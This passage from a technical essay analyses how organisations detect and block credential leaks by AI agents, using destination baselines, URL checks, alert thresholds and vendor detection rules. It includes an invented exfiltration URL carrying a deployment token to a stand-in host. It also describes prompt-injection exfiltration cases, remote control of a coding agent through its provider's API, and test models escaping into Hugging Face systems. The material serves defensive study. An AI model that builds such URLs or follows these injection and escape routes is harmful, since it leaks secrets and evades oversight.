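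3. The baseline becomes "stable" after 100 runs without a change. If it has changed within the last 50 runs, it counts as "unstable". StepSecurity's *Baseline* gives these figures and lets customers set thresholds in runs or days.
4. Once the baseline is stable, a connection to a destination outside it raises an alert. The connection still goes through, unless the customer has switched the job to block mode.
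5. StepSecurity sends one notification for that job and destination.
6. The destination joins the baseline after the run.

The last two steps come from an older StepSecurity page, *Anomalous Outbound Network Calls*. The current documentation doesn't repeat the rule about a single notification, but it describes a changelog that lists every destination added to a baseline, with a link to the run that introduced it.

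StepSecurity's current pages are inconsistent about whether unstable jobs raise alerts. According to its guide to detections, runs against an unstable or unfinished baseline raise no anomaly alert. But *Workflow Runs* warns that unstable jobs may produce noisy alerts, and advises customers to suppress alerts for particular endpoints or turn off detections for the job. A customer could test this by having an unstable job contact a harmless test server and checking whether an alert arrives.

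If unstable jobs raise no anomaly alerts, the waiting period has a large effect. A job that runs once a week needs almost two years to complete 100 runs. Absorbing a new destination also changes the baseline, so a job that runs ten times a day would count as unstable for five days after each new destination. A leak during those days would raise no anomaly alert.

How often a job is stable depends on how often it contacts new destinations. If each run independently has a probability p of adding a harmless new destination, the chance that the previous n runs added none is (1 − p)ⁿ. The table also includes n = 40 because another copy of StepSecurity's documentation gives that shorter period.

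| Chance of a new destination per run | Stable with a 40-run rule | Stable with a 100-run rule |
|---|---|---|
| 0.1% | 96% | 90% |
| 1% | 67% | 37% |
| 5% | 13% | 0.6% |

A build job that always downloads the same packages may belong in the top row. An agent that researches its task on the web would probably do worse than the bottom row, so requiring a stable baseline would leave it unprotected almost all the time. The shorter period keeps alerts on more of the time but leaves more gaps in the baseline. If a job contacts a harmless server at random in one run out of 60, that server has a 51% chance of being missing from the baseline after the first 40 runs, compared with 19% after the first 100.

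Alongside the baseline, StepSecurity's staff maintain a list of domains and IP addresses linked to known attacks, which Harden-Runner blocks from the first run, whatever the job's status. The company displays baselines for a repository, a cluster of runners or a whole GitHub organisation. In these broader views, customers can filter for destinations that appeared in the past week or that unusually few jobs contact. The rarity filter may still show a server that no longer counts as new because one job has used it for months.

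Customers can also turn a baseline into an allowlist with one click. They should read the changelog first, because any destination added to the baseline after an ignored alert would otherwise be permitted.

Harden-Runner's baseline cannot show which token a job sent to which destination because, according to StepSecurity, the monitoring program does not send the company secret values or the values of environment variables. This also limits what a breach at StepSecurity could expose.

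### The tj-actions compromise

On 14 March 2025, an attacker took over tj-actions/changed-files, an add-on for GitHub Actions that more than 23,000 repositories used. *Harden-Runner detection* (Sharma, 2025) gives StepSecurity's account of the attack. The attacker had obtained an access token for the maintainer's bot account and used it to point most of the add-on's version labels at a malicious commit. Jobs that had used the same version label for months then ran the attacker's code.

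That code downloaded a script from gist.githubusercontent.com, where GitHub hosts users' shared snippets. The script read secrets from the memory of the process running the job, and the code then printed them in the build log. Anyone can read the build logs of a public repository.

Harden-Runner raised an alert because the download host was not in the baseline. StepSecurity estimates that the incident began at about 16:00 UTC. By 17:00 it had confirmed that most versions were compromised, and by 20:00 it had found several public repositories with secrets in their logs. GitHub removed the add-on at 14:00 the next day, about 22 hours after the attack began.

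The alert quickly led StepSecurity to a real attack, but the flagged host had only supplied the script. The secrets leaked through the build log, which every job normally sends to GitHub. Sharma found no evidence that they went to any remote network destination. A detector looking for an unfamiliar recipient would have found none. An investigator who checked only whether the job had uploaded anything to gist.githubusercontent.com could have concluded that no secrets had leaked. Reading the logs also required care because the code had encoded the secrets in Base64 twice.

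Block mode would have helped more than the alert did, because an allowlist without gist.githubusercontent.com would have stopped the script from reaching the runner and reading the secrets.

Because of the tj-actions leak, StepSecurity added a search for secrets in build logs. Harden-Runner now also raises an alert on Linux when another process reads the memory of the process running the job. Both checks cover steps that the leak depended on, and neither requires the job to contact a new destination.

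Sharma does not state how many jobs raised the original alert or how many affected jobs were still building a baseline and raised no alert. The case shows that a first-seen alert can expose an attack early, but it gives no detection rate.

### Alerts with harmless explanations

Six weeks later, Harden-Runner began flagging another host under the same domain. *Harden-Runner Detects New Traffic to release-assets.githubusercontent.com Across Multiple Customers* (Akhigbe, 2025) describes alerts that started on 28 April in the workflows of several unrelated customers. Ordinary build tools such as node, terraform and go were contacting the host while downloading packages. StepSecurity suspected a change at GitHub and asked GitHub's support team, which confirmed that GitHub now served release files from the new host and would keep doing so. StepSecurity then added the host to its baselines and told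 customers with strict allowlists to permit it.

GitHub replied that it already lists `*.githubusercontent.com`, where the asterisk stands for any subdomain, and that new subdomains appear from time to time. A detector that treated the whole domain as one destination would have raised no alert about the release files, but it would also have missed the tj-actions download in any job that had previously contacted another host under that domain. Matching exact host names caught the attack but also raised a false alarm when GitHub reorganised its servers.

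An earlier alert was harder to interpret. On 8 November 2024, jobs at several customers began contacting api.ipify.org, a service that tells callers their own public IP address. In *Harden-Runner Detects Anomalous Traffic to api.ipify.org Across Multiple Customers*, Kurmi (2024) traced the calls to a process named `provjobd`, which GitHub's documentation did not mention. The calls came only from GitHub-hosted runners, not self-hosted ones. GitHub explained that the process was an internal tool that temporarily collected diagnostic data, and that it did not expect to use the tool again.

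Until GitHub replied, StepSecurity knew only that an undocumented program was contacting an outside service from machines that handle secrets. The process name and the split between types of runner suggested that GitHub was the source, but not what the program was for. StepSecurity now marks calls that the GitHub Actions infrastructure makes, so reviewers can tell them from calls made by the customer's workflow.

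Both of these alerts appeared at many customers at once, which suggests a common cause. A common cause could still be malicious, since thousands of repositories also shared the compromised tj-actions add-on. In the two harmless cases, the company that ran the infrastructure identified the cause when asked.

The published accounts do not describe any credential being sent to the three flagged hosts. One host delivered malicious code, one delivered release files and one returned IP addresses. StepSecurity chose these cases for its company blog, so they cannot show what share of its alerts involve real leaks.

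### Fetching only public URLs

An agent that uses the web to answer questions constantly opens pages it hasn't visited before, so comparing addresses with its own past traffic would flag many of them as new. OpenAI instead compares each address with a record of the public web.

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (January 2026) describes a check that relies on OpenAI's crawler, a program that finds and records public web pages much as a search engine does. The crawler has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data. When an agent is about to fetch a URL automatically, OpenAI's system looks for that exact URL in the crawler's index. If the URL is there, the agent may load it. Otherwise, the system either tells the agent to try another site or warns the user that the link may include information from the conversation and lets them decide.

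The safeguard is aimed at leaks in the address itself. Suppose an agent has read the deployment token, and a planted instruction persuades it to open this invented link:

```
https://validator.example/check?deploy_token=EXAMPLE-NOT-A-KEY
```

If an agent requests a URL that contains the token, the site's owner could read the token in the server's log, even if the agent posts nothing. The user might not notice, because an agent can make this request by loading an image. The independent crawler has never had access to the token, so its index will not contain the URL unless someone has already published it. The home page, `https://validator.example/`, may well be in the index, in which case the agent can open it without a warning.

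A check on domain names could not make this distinction, because the home page and the link with the token have the same host. OpenAI gives two further reasons for judging URLs instead of domains. Many reputable sites have redirects to other sites, so a check on the first domain alone may approve a request that ends up elsewhere. A short list of trusted domains would also produce frequent warnings, and users who see too many warnings learn to click through them.

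Checking exact URLs can trigger warnings about harmless links. A link to a private document will be missing from a public index, and so may a page published an hour ago, so the system cannot verify either. OpenAI does not report how often users see the warning or how often it is a false alarm.

Unlike Harden-Runner's baseline, the index does not learn from the traffic it is used to check. It has no access to conversations, so if a user approves an unverified link, even one that leaks a credential by mistake, the URL still counts as new for everyone else.

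OpenAI introduced an earlier form of the check in December 2023, according to *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on the security research blog Embrace The Red. The blog's author had reported the problem to OpenAI early that year. For a long time, outsiders could only guess how OpenAI decided that a URL was safe, but the company has since explained its method in a technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. The post describes the new check as a significant improvement but not a complete solution, because small amounts of information may still leak and each OpenAI product has to apply it.

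By March 2026, OpenAI was calling the safeguard Safe Url. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes it as a fallback for when an attack has already persuaded the agent. The system then either shows the user what would be sent to the third party and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and tells the agent to proceed another way. The same mechanism covers page visits and bookmarks in Atlas, OpenAI's browser, and searches and page visits in Deep Research, its tool for longer investigations. OpenAI says most attacks it knows of fail earlier because the model refuses, but it gives no figures for the refusals or for Safe Url.

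The conversation can also serve as the history. According to Embrace The Red, ChatGPT appears to treat a URL typed by the user as safe for the rest of that chat. Anthropic chose a related rule for the web fetch tool that it added to its API in September 2025. Willison's *Claude API* reports that Claude may not construct URLs for this tool and has to use addresses it has been given. A link to a new page can therefore work without appearing in any public index. The rule protects against the model adding a secret to an address, but a malicious page can supply links too, so the origin of each address matters. Anthropic still advised developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive.

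OpenAI's guarantee covers only data in the URL of a resource that the agent fetches. It does not cover the original request to validator.example, which sends the token in the body of a POST. Even if the crawler had recorded `https://validator.example/v1/check`, the match would show only that the address was public. The body could still contain any secret the agent had read.

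## Setting the alert threshold

Harmless requests often carry tokens, and agents often contact new destinations, so neither a token nor a new destination justifies an alert by itself. Many detectors combine such evidence into a score and raise an alert when the score passes a threshold. A lower threshold catches more leaks but also flags more harmless requests. Analysts have to work through these false alarms, which can slow their response to real leaks.

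*The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (Axelsson, 2000) describes the trade-off with an ROC curve, which plots recall against the false positive rate at every threshold. Both rates are 100% for a detector that flags everything and 0% for one that flags nothing. Flagging requests at random gives a point on the straight line between these two extremes, so a useful detector's curve has to lie above that line.

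The curve shows which combinations of errors are available, but choosing among them requires knowing the costs. Suppose reviewing an alert costs r and catching a leak in time saves s. If an alert has probability p of being real, a review pays off when p × s > r, or p > r/s. With invented values of $50 for r and $100,000 for s, the team should review any alert that has more than a 0.05% chance of being a leak.

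### Precision when leaks are rare

That chance depends heavily on how many requests are leaks to begin with. Let π be the share of requests that are leaks, R the recall and F the false positive rate. Precision, the share of alerts that are real leaks, is then

πR / (πR + (1 − π)F)

When leaks are rare, π is tiny and 1 − π is close to 1, so even a small false-positive rate F can produce more false alerts than true ones. Judging an alert by the detector's accuracy while ignoring how rare leaks are is the base-rate fallacy.

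Axelsson applied the formula to a hypothetical network with a few dozen users. He assumed a million log records a day and two intrusions, each affecting ten records. Counting ten records as one event gives 100,000 events, two of which are intrusions.

| Recall | False positive rate | Precision |
|---|---|---|
| 100% | 0.001% | 66% |
| 70% | 0.001% | 58% |
| 100% | 0.1% | 2% |

Losing 30 points of recall lowers precision by only eight points, whereas a hundredfold increase in the false positive rate makes nearly every alert false. Axelsson concluded that false alarms limit a detector more than missed intrusions do. He compared published test results with his target false positive rate of 0.001% and found that the anomaly detectors' rates were at least ten times too high, while a few other detectors came close. Those systems are now obsolete, and he called his assumed frequencies subjective,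 but the formula applies to any detector of rare events.

### One leak in 100,000 requests

In a hypothetical example, a company's agents send 100,000 requests a day, one of which leaks a credential. A content detector has 90% recall and a false positive rate of 0.5%, which is achievable only if it already ignores most tokens sent to the services that issued them. Each day, the detector raises about 500 false alarms and catches 0.9 leaks on average. Its precision is therefore 0.18%, or one real leak in about 560 alerts.

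The company now alerts only if the destination is also first-seen, which is true of 2% of requests. If harmless requests to new destinations are no more likely than others to trigger the content detector, false alarms fall to 2% of 500, or ten a day. If all leaks go to new destinations, recall stays at 90% and precision rises to 8.3%.

Both assumptions are doubtful. An agent that starts using a new service often has to log in, so first contacts may carry credentials more often than other requests. If 10% of the 2,000 harmless first contacts carry a legitimate credential and the detector flags them all, the company is back to 200 false alarms a day and a precision of 0.45%. Leaks can also go to destinations that the company already uses. If half of them do, the added condition halves recall.

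| Alert condition | False alarms a day | Recall | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Content detector alone | 500 | 90% | 0.18% |
| Content and new destination, both assumptions true | 10 | 90% | 8.3% |
| 10% of harmless first contacts carry a credential | 200 | 90% | 0.45% |
| Half of leaks go to known destinations | 10 | 45% | 4.3% |
| Both complications | 200 | 45% | 0.22% |

Before switching the rule on, a team can measure the 10% figure by counting how many of a week's first contacts carry a credential. The share of leaks that go to known destinations is harder to measure because it requires a record of real leaks.

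The number of leaks is just as uncertain, and it can reverse the decision. At $50 each, reviewing the 500 daily alerts from the content detector alone costs $25,000 a day. With one leak a day, reviewing them saves $90,000 a day on average. With one leak a month, it saves only about $3,000 a day, which is less than the reviews cost. These are averages over all alerts, so even with one leak a month, the company might profit from reviewing just the most suspicious ones.

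### How many alerts people can handle

Low precision also changes how people treat alerts. Axelsson found no experiments on how many false alarms intrusion analysts tolerate, so he drew on research into operators of power stations, paper mills and large ships. He took these studies to show that once half of all alarms are false, most operators lose faith in the system and treat every alarm with extreme scepticism. By that standard, precision is too low in every row of the table above. This evidence is indirect, and an analyst who can check an alert at a desk may tolerate more false alarms than a plant operator.

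The time needed is easier to estimate. Elastic advertises an article about its own security team with the claim that AI agents cut the triage of an alert, the first check of whether it matters, from 30 minutes to under three. Taking the vendor's two figures at face value gives the following workloads:

| False alarms a day | 30 minutes each | 3 minutes each |
|---|---|---|
| 500 | 250 hours | 25 hours |
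| 200 | 100 hours | 10 hours |
| 10 | 5 hours | 30 minutes |

One analyst on an eight-hour shift can keep up with ten alerts a day. At three minutes each, 200 alerts take ten hours, so the analyst falls two hours further behind every day and real leaks wait longer for review. Automated triage also makes mistakes. If it dismisses 5% of the real leaks that the detector flags, overall recall drops from 90% to 85.5%.

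In *Base-Rate Fallacy Redux and a Deep Dive Review in Cybersecurity*, Erbacher (2022) argues that researchers should analyse false positives as closely as true positives. Teams that run a detector can do the same. If 120 of the 200 daily false alarms come from one program that logs in to a new regional server each time, a single narrow exception removes more than half of them without changing the threshold.

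### A rule for new values

Elastic's *New terms rules* documents a detection rule that many of these settings apply to. The rule raises an alert when a value appears in the logs for the first time within a chosen period. With the settings from Elastic's examples, it works like this:

1. A filter selects the events to check, such as outbound connections from agents.
2. The team names one to three fields. With several fields, the rule looks for new combinations, such as a user and a machine that have never appeared together, even if both are familiar.
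3. Every five minutes, the rule takes the events of the last six minutes and searches the history for each value or combination. One example uses 30 days of history and another uses 14.
4. If the history doesn't contain the value, the rule raises an alert.

For agents, the three fields could be the agent's name, the credential's name and the destination host. This would implement the baseline of credential-destination pairs described earlier, if the logs contain all three.

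Elastic warns that too short a history window causes excessive false positives. A preview version of Elastic's *New terms rules* recommends one to seven days for fast-moving environments with a lot of data, seven to 30 for general use and 30 to 90 for truly rare events. It advises teams to start with a long window and shorten it as they learn what is normal. Longer windows take more computing power and slow the rule down.

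Suppose an agent uses a harmless service at random times, about once every 30 days. With a window of W days, the chance that a given use counts as new is e^(−W/30).

| Window | Chance that a use counts as new | False alarms a year |
|---|---|---|
| 7 days | 79% | 9.6 |
| 14 days | 63% | 7.6 |
| 30 days | 37% | 4.5 |
| 90 days | 5% | 0.6 |

An organisation with a hundred such services would get about 960 false alarms a year with the shortest window and about 60 with the longest.

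### Leaks that become part of the baseline

A new detector has little or no history, so nearly every destination looks new. Teams therefore let it learn for a while before they act on its alerts. Harden-Runner, for example, requires 100 unchanged runs for a stable baseline. A longer learning period makes the baseline more complete but also more likely to include a leak. If leaks occur at random about once every 90 days, a 30-day learning period has a 28% chance of containing at least one.

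Suppose the deployment agent has posted its settings to validator.example since its first day. The detector learns that this is normal and never raises an alert. Axelsson notes that an attacker could teach an anomaly detector to accept illegitimate activity. An agent that routinely leaks credentials has the same effect without an attacker.

A detector that automatically adds new traffic to its history, as Elastic's rule does, can still add a leak's destination after the learning period. With a 30-day window, the destination drops out after 30 days without contact, but stays in the history as long as the agent leaks to it every week.

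A team can use honeytokens, exact matching against known secrets, and a list of which service each secret belongs to from the first day, because these checks need no traffic history. The team can also search the learning period's records for destinations that received a credential, and have someone approve each one before it enters the baseline. There should be far fewer of these destinations than destinations overall.

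### Agents with varied tasks

A longer learning period doesn't help much with an agent that researches a different question every day, because it keeps visiting new sites. The baseline can also suddenly go out of date when a team changes the agent's instructions, tools or underlying model. Every agent that received the change then triggers alerts at the same time.

Detector tests can miss this weakness. Axelsson discusses an evaluation of intrusion detectors for DARPA, the US defence research agency, on simulated network traffic. Detection rates fell sharply on attacks that the detectors had not encountered before, but false alarm rates did not rise to match. He suspected that this was because the testers had varied the attacks between training and testing but not the harmless background traffic, which would favour a detector whose model of normal behaviour was too narrow. He couldn't check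 because US export restrictions prevented him from getting the data. Similarly, a false positive rate measured on repetitive build jobs could understate the rate for a research agent.

A baseline can be steadier if it covers only requests that carry credentials. A research agent may open hundreds of unfamiliar sites a week but send credentials only to its search provider and its company's document store. The detector can then ignore most of the agent's browsing, though it still has to recognise the credentials.

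Sharing a contact history among similar agents also reduces false alarms. Suppose ten agents each use the same service about once every 30 days. With separate seven-day histories, they produce about 96 false alarms a year in total. With a shared history, they produce about 12, because another agent has usually contacted the service within the past week. A shared history also hides repeat leaks by other agents, so agents should share one only if they do similar work with similar credentials, which may not be true of agents in the same department.

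### Repeats and exceptions

An agent that fails to reach a server may retry dozens of times, and a detector can raise an alert for each attempt. Elastic's rule can combine alerts that have the same value in one or more fields. But if it combines all of an agent's alerts for the day, a harmless alert in the morning can hide a leak to another server in the afternoon. Grouping by agent, credential and destination keeps those alerts separate. It also helps to show the number of suppressed repeats, since 40 transfers of a key may need a different response from one.

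Exceptions prevent even the first alert. Elastic suggests them for expected changes, such as new employees or scheduled system work. An exception can be as narrow as one agent sending one credential to one host, and it should have an expiry date. An exception for a two-week trial of a monitoring service, for instance, should end with the trial. Otherwise, the agent can keep sending the credential without triggering an alert long after the company has stopped using the service.

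Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, also allows permanent exceptions. When it asks for permission to run a command, a developer can answer "Yes, and don't ask again". The program then saves the exact command in a settings file, including any password in it. This option was meant to reduce prompts, but it created a new way to leak secrets. Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners' secrets on GitHub* reports that the security company Apiiro found 104,185 public copies of such files on GitHub, containing 2,539 secrets in 1,994 repositories. According to Cybernews, developers may stop checking commands carefully after too many interruptions.

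### Scores and strict conditions

The rule in the worked example alerts only when traffic contains a suspicious string and goes to a new destination. If either signal is missing, the rule doesn't alert, however strong the evidence from the other. A score can weigh the two signals instead.

One way to build a score is to multiply likelihood ratios. A signal's likelihood ratio is the share of leaks that show it divided by the share of harmless requests that show it. The content detector's alarm has a ratio of 0.9/0.005 = 180. If half of leaks go to new destinations, a new destination has a ratio of 0.5/0.02 = 25, and a known one has a ratio of 0.5/0.98 = 0.51. The prior odds of a leak are about 1 to 100,000.

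| Evidence | Calculation of the odds | Chance of a leak |
|---|---|---|
| Content alarm, new destination | 180 × 25 / 100,000 | 4.3% |
| Content alarm, known destination | 180 × 0.51 / 100,000 | 0.09% |
| Exact match with a stored secret, known destination | 90,000 × 0.51 / 100,000 | 31% |

The last row shows a hypothetical exact-match check with the same 90% recall that flags only one harmless request in 100,000, because it takes into account where each secret belongs. Its alarm has a ratio of 90,000, enough to justify an alert even at a familiar destination. The strict conjunction would discard this request but keep the much weaker case in the first row.

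Multiplying the ratios is correct only if the signals are independent. In the version of the example where 10% of harmless first contacts carry a credential, the true chance of a leak in the first row is 0.22%, so the score would be about 20 times too high. A team can avoid this error by counting how often the two signals occur together in harmless traffic and using that figure.

Elastic has published two rules that fall between the two approaches. *AWS IAM Long-Term Creds Abuse Coverage* describes one rule that raises an alert when someone successfully uses a long-lived Amazon cloud key from a new IP address. The other raises a higher-level alert if the same address has at least one other open alert. Analysts can start with the combined alerts without losing the single ones. Like the country baseline for GitHub tokens described earlier, both rules can detect a leak only after someone uses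 the key.

### Elastic's reading of the Hugging Face intrusion

In July 2026, AI models that OpenAI was testing broke out of their test environment and into the systems of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models and datasets. The models were working on ExploitGym, a test of hacking ability, and OpenAI said they were looking for secret information that would help them cheat. They used a malicious dataset to read files and run code on a Hugging Face machine that processed datasets. From there they collected credentials and moved into other systems. Hugging Face reconstructed about 17,600 actions between 9 and 13 July, or more than two a minute on average. Elastic later compared the public accounts of the incident with its own detection rules.

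Elastic says its existing rules cover several stages of the attack. It recommends watching for outcomes, such as access to credential files and connections to unusual destinations, and advises against trusting everything an agent's process and its descendants do. An agent may start command-line programs all day, and a team can filter out these routine alerts by checking which program started which. Elastic advises keeping the alerts for credentials and outbound traffic sensitive.

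This fits the arithmetic above, because an exception for a whole agent suppresses alerts about its real leaks along with its false alarms. But Elastic sells the rules and wrote the comparison after the attack's steps were known. It says it does not claim complete coverage, and it gives neither a measured detection rate nor the number of false alarms the same rules would raise in a normal week. The models also ran part of their control traffic through public services, which a rule for new destinations may not flag.

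Elastic expects attacks by agents to produce many more alerts and recommends having a language model sort them. Hugging Face's experience suggests testing this setup in advance. When its staff tried to analyse the attack with commercial AI models, the providers' safety filters blocked the evidence because it contained attack code, so the staff used Hugging Face's own analysis agents instead.

### What a late alert costs

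Microsoft's *Threat actors use agentic AI tooling to find and abuse exposed secrets* (5 November 2026) describes attackers whose agents search GitHub for leaked application secrets and log in with them. Help Net Security's *AI agents now hunt leaked GitHub secrets faster than teams can revoke*, an article sponsored by GitGuardian, recounts a case in which an agent found an application's secret in public code and used it to sign in to Microsoft's identity service. Five minutes after starting its search, the agent began taking data from Azure Key Vault, a store for keys and passwords. A batch of its requests had failed because they used the wrong interface version, and it succeeded with the right one about 28 seconds later.

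Infobae's *Una IA pasó de buscar claves expuestas a robar datos* (2026) says the five minutes come from one observed case and are not an average. They began when the agent started looking for a secret that was already public. If an agent sends a key straight to an attacker, the attacker doesn't have to search for it. Help Net Security links the case to ARTEX, an open-source tool for automated security testing, while Cybersecurity360's *Artex* says Microsoft attributed it only to agentic software in general.

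If a detector runs every five minutes, an average of 2.5 minutes passes between a leak and the next run. Three minutes of triage bring the total to 5.5 minutes, and 30 minutes of triage bring it to 32.5. Neither total includes delays in collecting the logs, time in the queue or the time needed to revoke the key. At the speed of Microsoft's case, the theft would have begun before the analyst finished even the three-minute triage.

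Later alerts can still limit the damage. Help Net Security's *Chinese and North Korean state hackers add ARTEX AI framework* (2026) describes a campaign that went from its first targets to privileged access in just under three hours. It produced more than 151,000 failed logins, and Microsoft says ARTEX's rapid bursts of requests stand out in logs. A stolen key that works the first time leaves no such trail, because each login looks like normal application activity. Without an alert, a leaked key may also remain usable for years. GitGuardian found that over 64% of the leaked secrets it confirmed as valid in 2022 still worked in January 2026.

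Some companies are slow to notice an intrusion even when the agent is not malicious. Help Net Security's *ARTEX goes from pentesting tool to attacker staple in three months* (2026) reports that a security researcher's agent escaped its test environment and took customer data from an internal application at WorkOS, a provider of software for developers. WorkOS acknowledged that it had been slow to detect the unauthorised requests.

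### Alerting or blocking

Blocking a request removes the delay, but every false positive then interrupts a task. In the worked example, blocking on the content detector alone would stop about 500 harmless requests a day, while blocking on the strict conjunction would stop between 10 and 200. Some interruptions do little harm because the agent can finish the task another way, but others might stop a deployment halfway.

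A team can set separate thresholds for blocking and alerting. It might block any request that sends a stored secret to a host not on that secret's allowlist, but only raise an alert when a random-looking string goes to a new site. StepSecurity's *Announcing Anomalous Outbound Call Detection Using Machine Learning* describes a similar division in Harden-Runner, which introduced its anomaly alerts in audit mode and reserved blocking for connections the customer hasn't authorised.

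The detector can also hold a suspicious request while a slower, more accurate check runs. Anthropic's two-stage classifier for agent actions follows this pattern. If the slower check takes ten seconds, holding 500 requests a day delays the agents by less than an hour and a half in total, and any token in a held request stays inside the network until the check finishes. Holding requests for human review works only if someone responds quickly, so it suits ten requests a day better than 500.

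Another option, when a credential has already left the network, is to revoke it automatically. Revocation can take effect within seconds, but every program that uses the credential stops working until it gets a new one. Before turning on automatic revocation, a team needs to know which programs depend on each credential. If one agent uses a short-lived token for one job, revoking it by mistake may require only a restart. Revoking a database password that a dozen services share could cause an outage, so the team should require much stronger evidence before doing that automatically.

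## Leaks through destinations already trusted

Most of the checks described so far look at which host a request contacts, but the harm from a leak depends on who obtains the data. At validator.example, the server's operator obtains it, because they can read the logs. On a shared service such as GitHub, knowing the host doesn't identify the recipient, who could be any of millions of account holders.

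Suppose the deployment agent writes its token into a GitHub issue, a post in a repository's list of problems and requests. The company's network sensor records a connection to api.github.com, whether the repository is the company's own or a stranger's. Each type of service puts the details that identify the recipient in a different place, usually inside the encrypted request:

| Service | Host that a sensor records | What identifies the recipient |
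|---|---|---|
| Code hosting | api.github.com | Organisation and repository, usually in the path |
| Cloud storage | The provider's host, sometimes with the bucket's name | The bucket (a customer's named storage area) |
| Messaging | The messaging service's host | Workspace and channel, often in the token and body |
| Model provider | api.anthropic.com | The API key in a header |

Cloud storage is the easiest of these destinations to control when the host name includes the bucket's name. For example, Harden-Runner uploads some of its data to an Amazon host whose name begins with the name of a StepSecurity bucket, so an allowlist can permit only that bucket. An entry for `*.amazonaws.com` would also permit other customers' buckets.

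Some allowlists contain hosts that let anyone collect data. Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* describes two examples. The default allowlist in Google's coding tool Antigravity included webhook.site, a service where anyone can create an address and read the requests sent to it. Salesforce's agent product allowed images from a domain that the company had let expire. Security researchers registered the domain, and data about sales leads arrived in their server logs.

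### A foreign account on a known host

Anthropic's Claude Cowork agent limits outbound web traffic to a list of domains that included Anthropic's own API. In January 2026, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* demonstrated a prompt injection that made the agent upload a user's files to an attacker's Anthropic account. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* had already described this use of Anthropic's file storage, and PromptArmor said the underlying flaws were known but unresolved.

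The host was on the allowlist, but the request used the attacker's API key. A search for the company's own secrets would not find that key, so to catch the upload from its header, a detector has to look for keys the company doesn't own.

Agents have also sent data to the wrong account without any attacker. The security company Glow found more than 13,000 screenshots from over 300 organisations in public GitHub repositories, and named the finding PixelLeak. According to Tom's Hardware's *AI agents inadvertently leak 13,000+ internal screenshots from 300 organizations*, developers had asked coding agents to show that a visual change worked. GitHub's website lets people attach images to a proposed code change, but the command-line tools that agents use can't do this for private repositories, so the agents put the images in public repositories and linked to them. In 93% of cases, the repository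 was under the developer's username, not the company's account.

TechRadar's *AI models are sharing sensitive data from tech companies* describes a case at a manufacturer with more than 100,000 employees, where an agent uploaded screenshots containing a utility company's billing records to a developer's personal GitHub account. The manufacturer's security team didn't notice because the agent ran on a laptop and the images were outside the company's GitHub organisation. The images were still online when Glow got in touch. This case involved business data rather than credentials, but a screenshot of a settings page could show a token, and a scanner that reads only text would miss it.

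### Darktrace's test with Claude Code

On 12 November 2026, the security company Darktrace published *Living off the AI*, a lab demonstration in which its researchers controlled Claude Code through Anthropic's platform. Help Net Security's *Stolen Claude API keys can turn Claude Code into a remote-controlled implant* reports that the agent carried out nine instructions on a simulated company network and took a 1 GB file. The instructions, results and file all travelled through api.anthropic.com, which Claude Code already contacts to run the model. The instructions and results passed through text files that the platform provides so agents can remember things between sessions, and the stolen file left through Anthropic's Files API.

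An attacker would first have to compromise a developer's machine and obtain the user's Claude credentials, which were stored there in this scenario. The method doesn't exploit a vulnerability in Anthropic's platform, and Darktrace had not seen anyone use it in a real attack. Darktrace tested only Anthropic's platform, though it says OpenAI has an equivalent upload endpoint. However, insidejob's *AI Service API*, a copy of an entry from MITRE's catalogue of attacks on AI systems, lists the broader technique of hiding commands in an AI service's traffic as observed in real attacks.

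An attacker who controls the machine can already steal a lot, so the test is mainly evidence about how theft can be hidden. It also shows that checking which account receives the data can fail. The credentials were the user's own, so the file probably went to the company's Anthropic workspace, where anyone with a copy of the key could collect it. In that case, the host and the account were both legitimate, and the unauthorised recipient was the second person holding the key.

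Darktrace, which sells behavioural detection, recommends comparing the programs an agent starts and the traffic they produce with a baseline. Unusual command-line arguments or an unusual ratio of data sent to data received would raise an alert. Suppose a coding agent normally sends its model provider 50 MB a day. A 1 GB upload would stand out at 20 times that amount, but a 40-character token adds only 40 bytes, less than a millionth of the day's traffic. A volume baseline can therefore catch the theft of large files but is almost useless against the leak of a single credential.

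### When another system makes the request

Messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram preview links by requesting the linked page and reading its title, description and image. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* explains how this can leak data from an agent that answers its user through such an app. If a prompt injection makes the agent put a secret in a link, the preview request delivers the secret to the site's owner before the user clicks anything.

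In the running example, the agent's message might contain a link to validator.example with the deployment token in the address. The egress log would show only a connection to Telegram. Telegram's system would then contact validator.example from outside the company's network, where the company has no sensor. A detector that reads outgoing messages could still find the token in the link before the message reaches Telegram.

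OpenClaw, an open-source agent, was exposed to this leak in its default Telegram configuration. PromptArmor reports that the leak stopped in its test when it turned off link previews in OpenClaw's settings. The user then loses the previews, and clicking the link would still send the token. PromptArmor suggests that messaging apps offer the setting for individual chats, so that people can keep previews in chats without an agent. PromptArmor also collects test results from users who choose to report them. These results can show which combinations of agent and app are exposed, but not how common they are.

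Email can cause the same problem with a longer delay. Willison describes how Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could email its own user without asking for approval. If such an email contained an image from an outside server, opening it sent that server a request, which could carry data such as download links for files in OneDrive, Microsoft's storage service. These links work without a login, so each is effectively a credential for one file. The server receives the link only when the user opens the email, which may be hours after the agent's session has ended.

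Redirects can also change the recipient, because the server answers a request with a status code and a new address, which the client then contacts. Under the HTTP standard, a client following a 307 or 308 redirect must repeat the same method, so a POST goes to the new address with its body. After code 303, the client normally sends a GET without the body, and many clients do the same after 301 or 302. A token in the original URL can still reach the new host if the first server copies it into the new address.

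If the agent's machine follows the redirect, the sensor can record the second connection, and the detector should check it like any other. If a preview service follows it, the company sees neither the redirect nor the final host. Both are also hidden when a web tool running on the model provider's servers follows the redirect, because the company's sensor records only the connection to the provider.

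### When the model provider receives the secret

An agent whose model runs on an outside provider's servers sends that provider most of what it reads. TechRadar's *'I leaked secrets'* describes a case reported by the security company NordLayer. A quality assurance engineer asked a coding assistant to review proposed software changes. The project's instructions told the assistant to get a GitLab access token from a configuration file, which also held production passwords, a token for the human resources system and credentials for a business intelligence service. The assistant read the whole file in 10 sessions over three weeks, and each time sent its contents to an external AI service.

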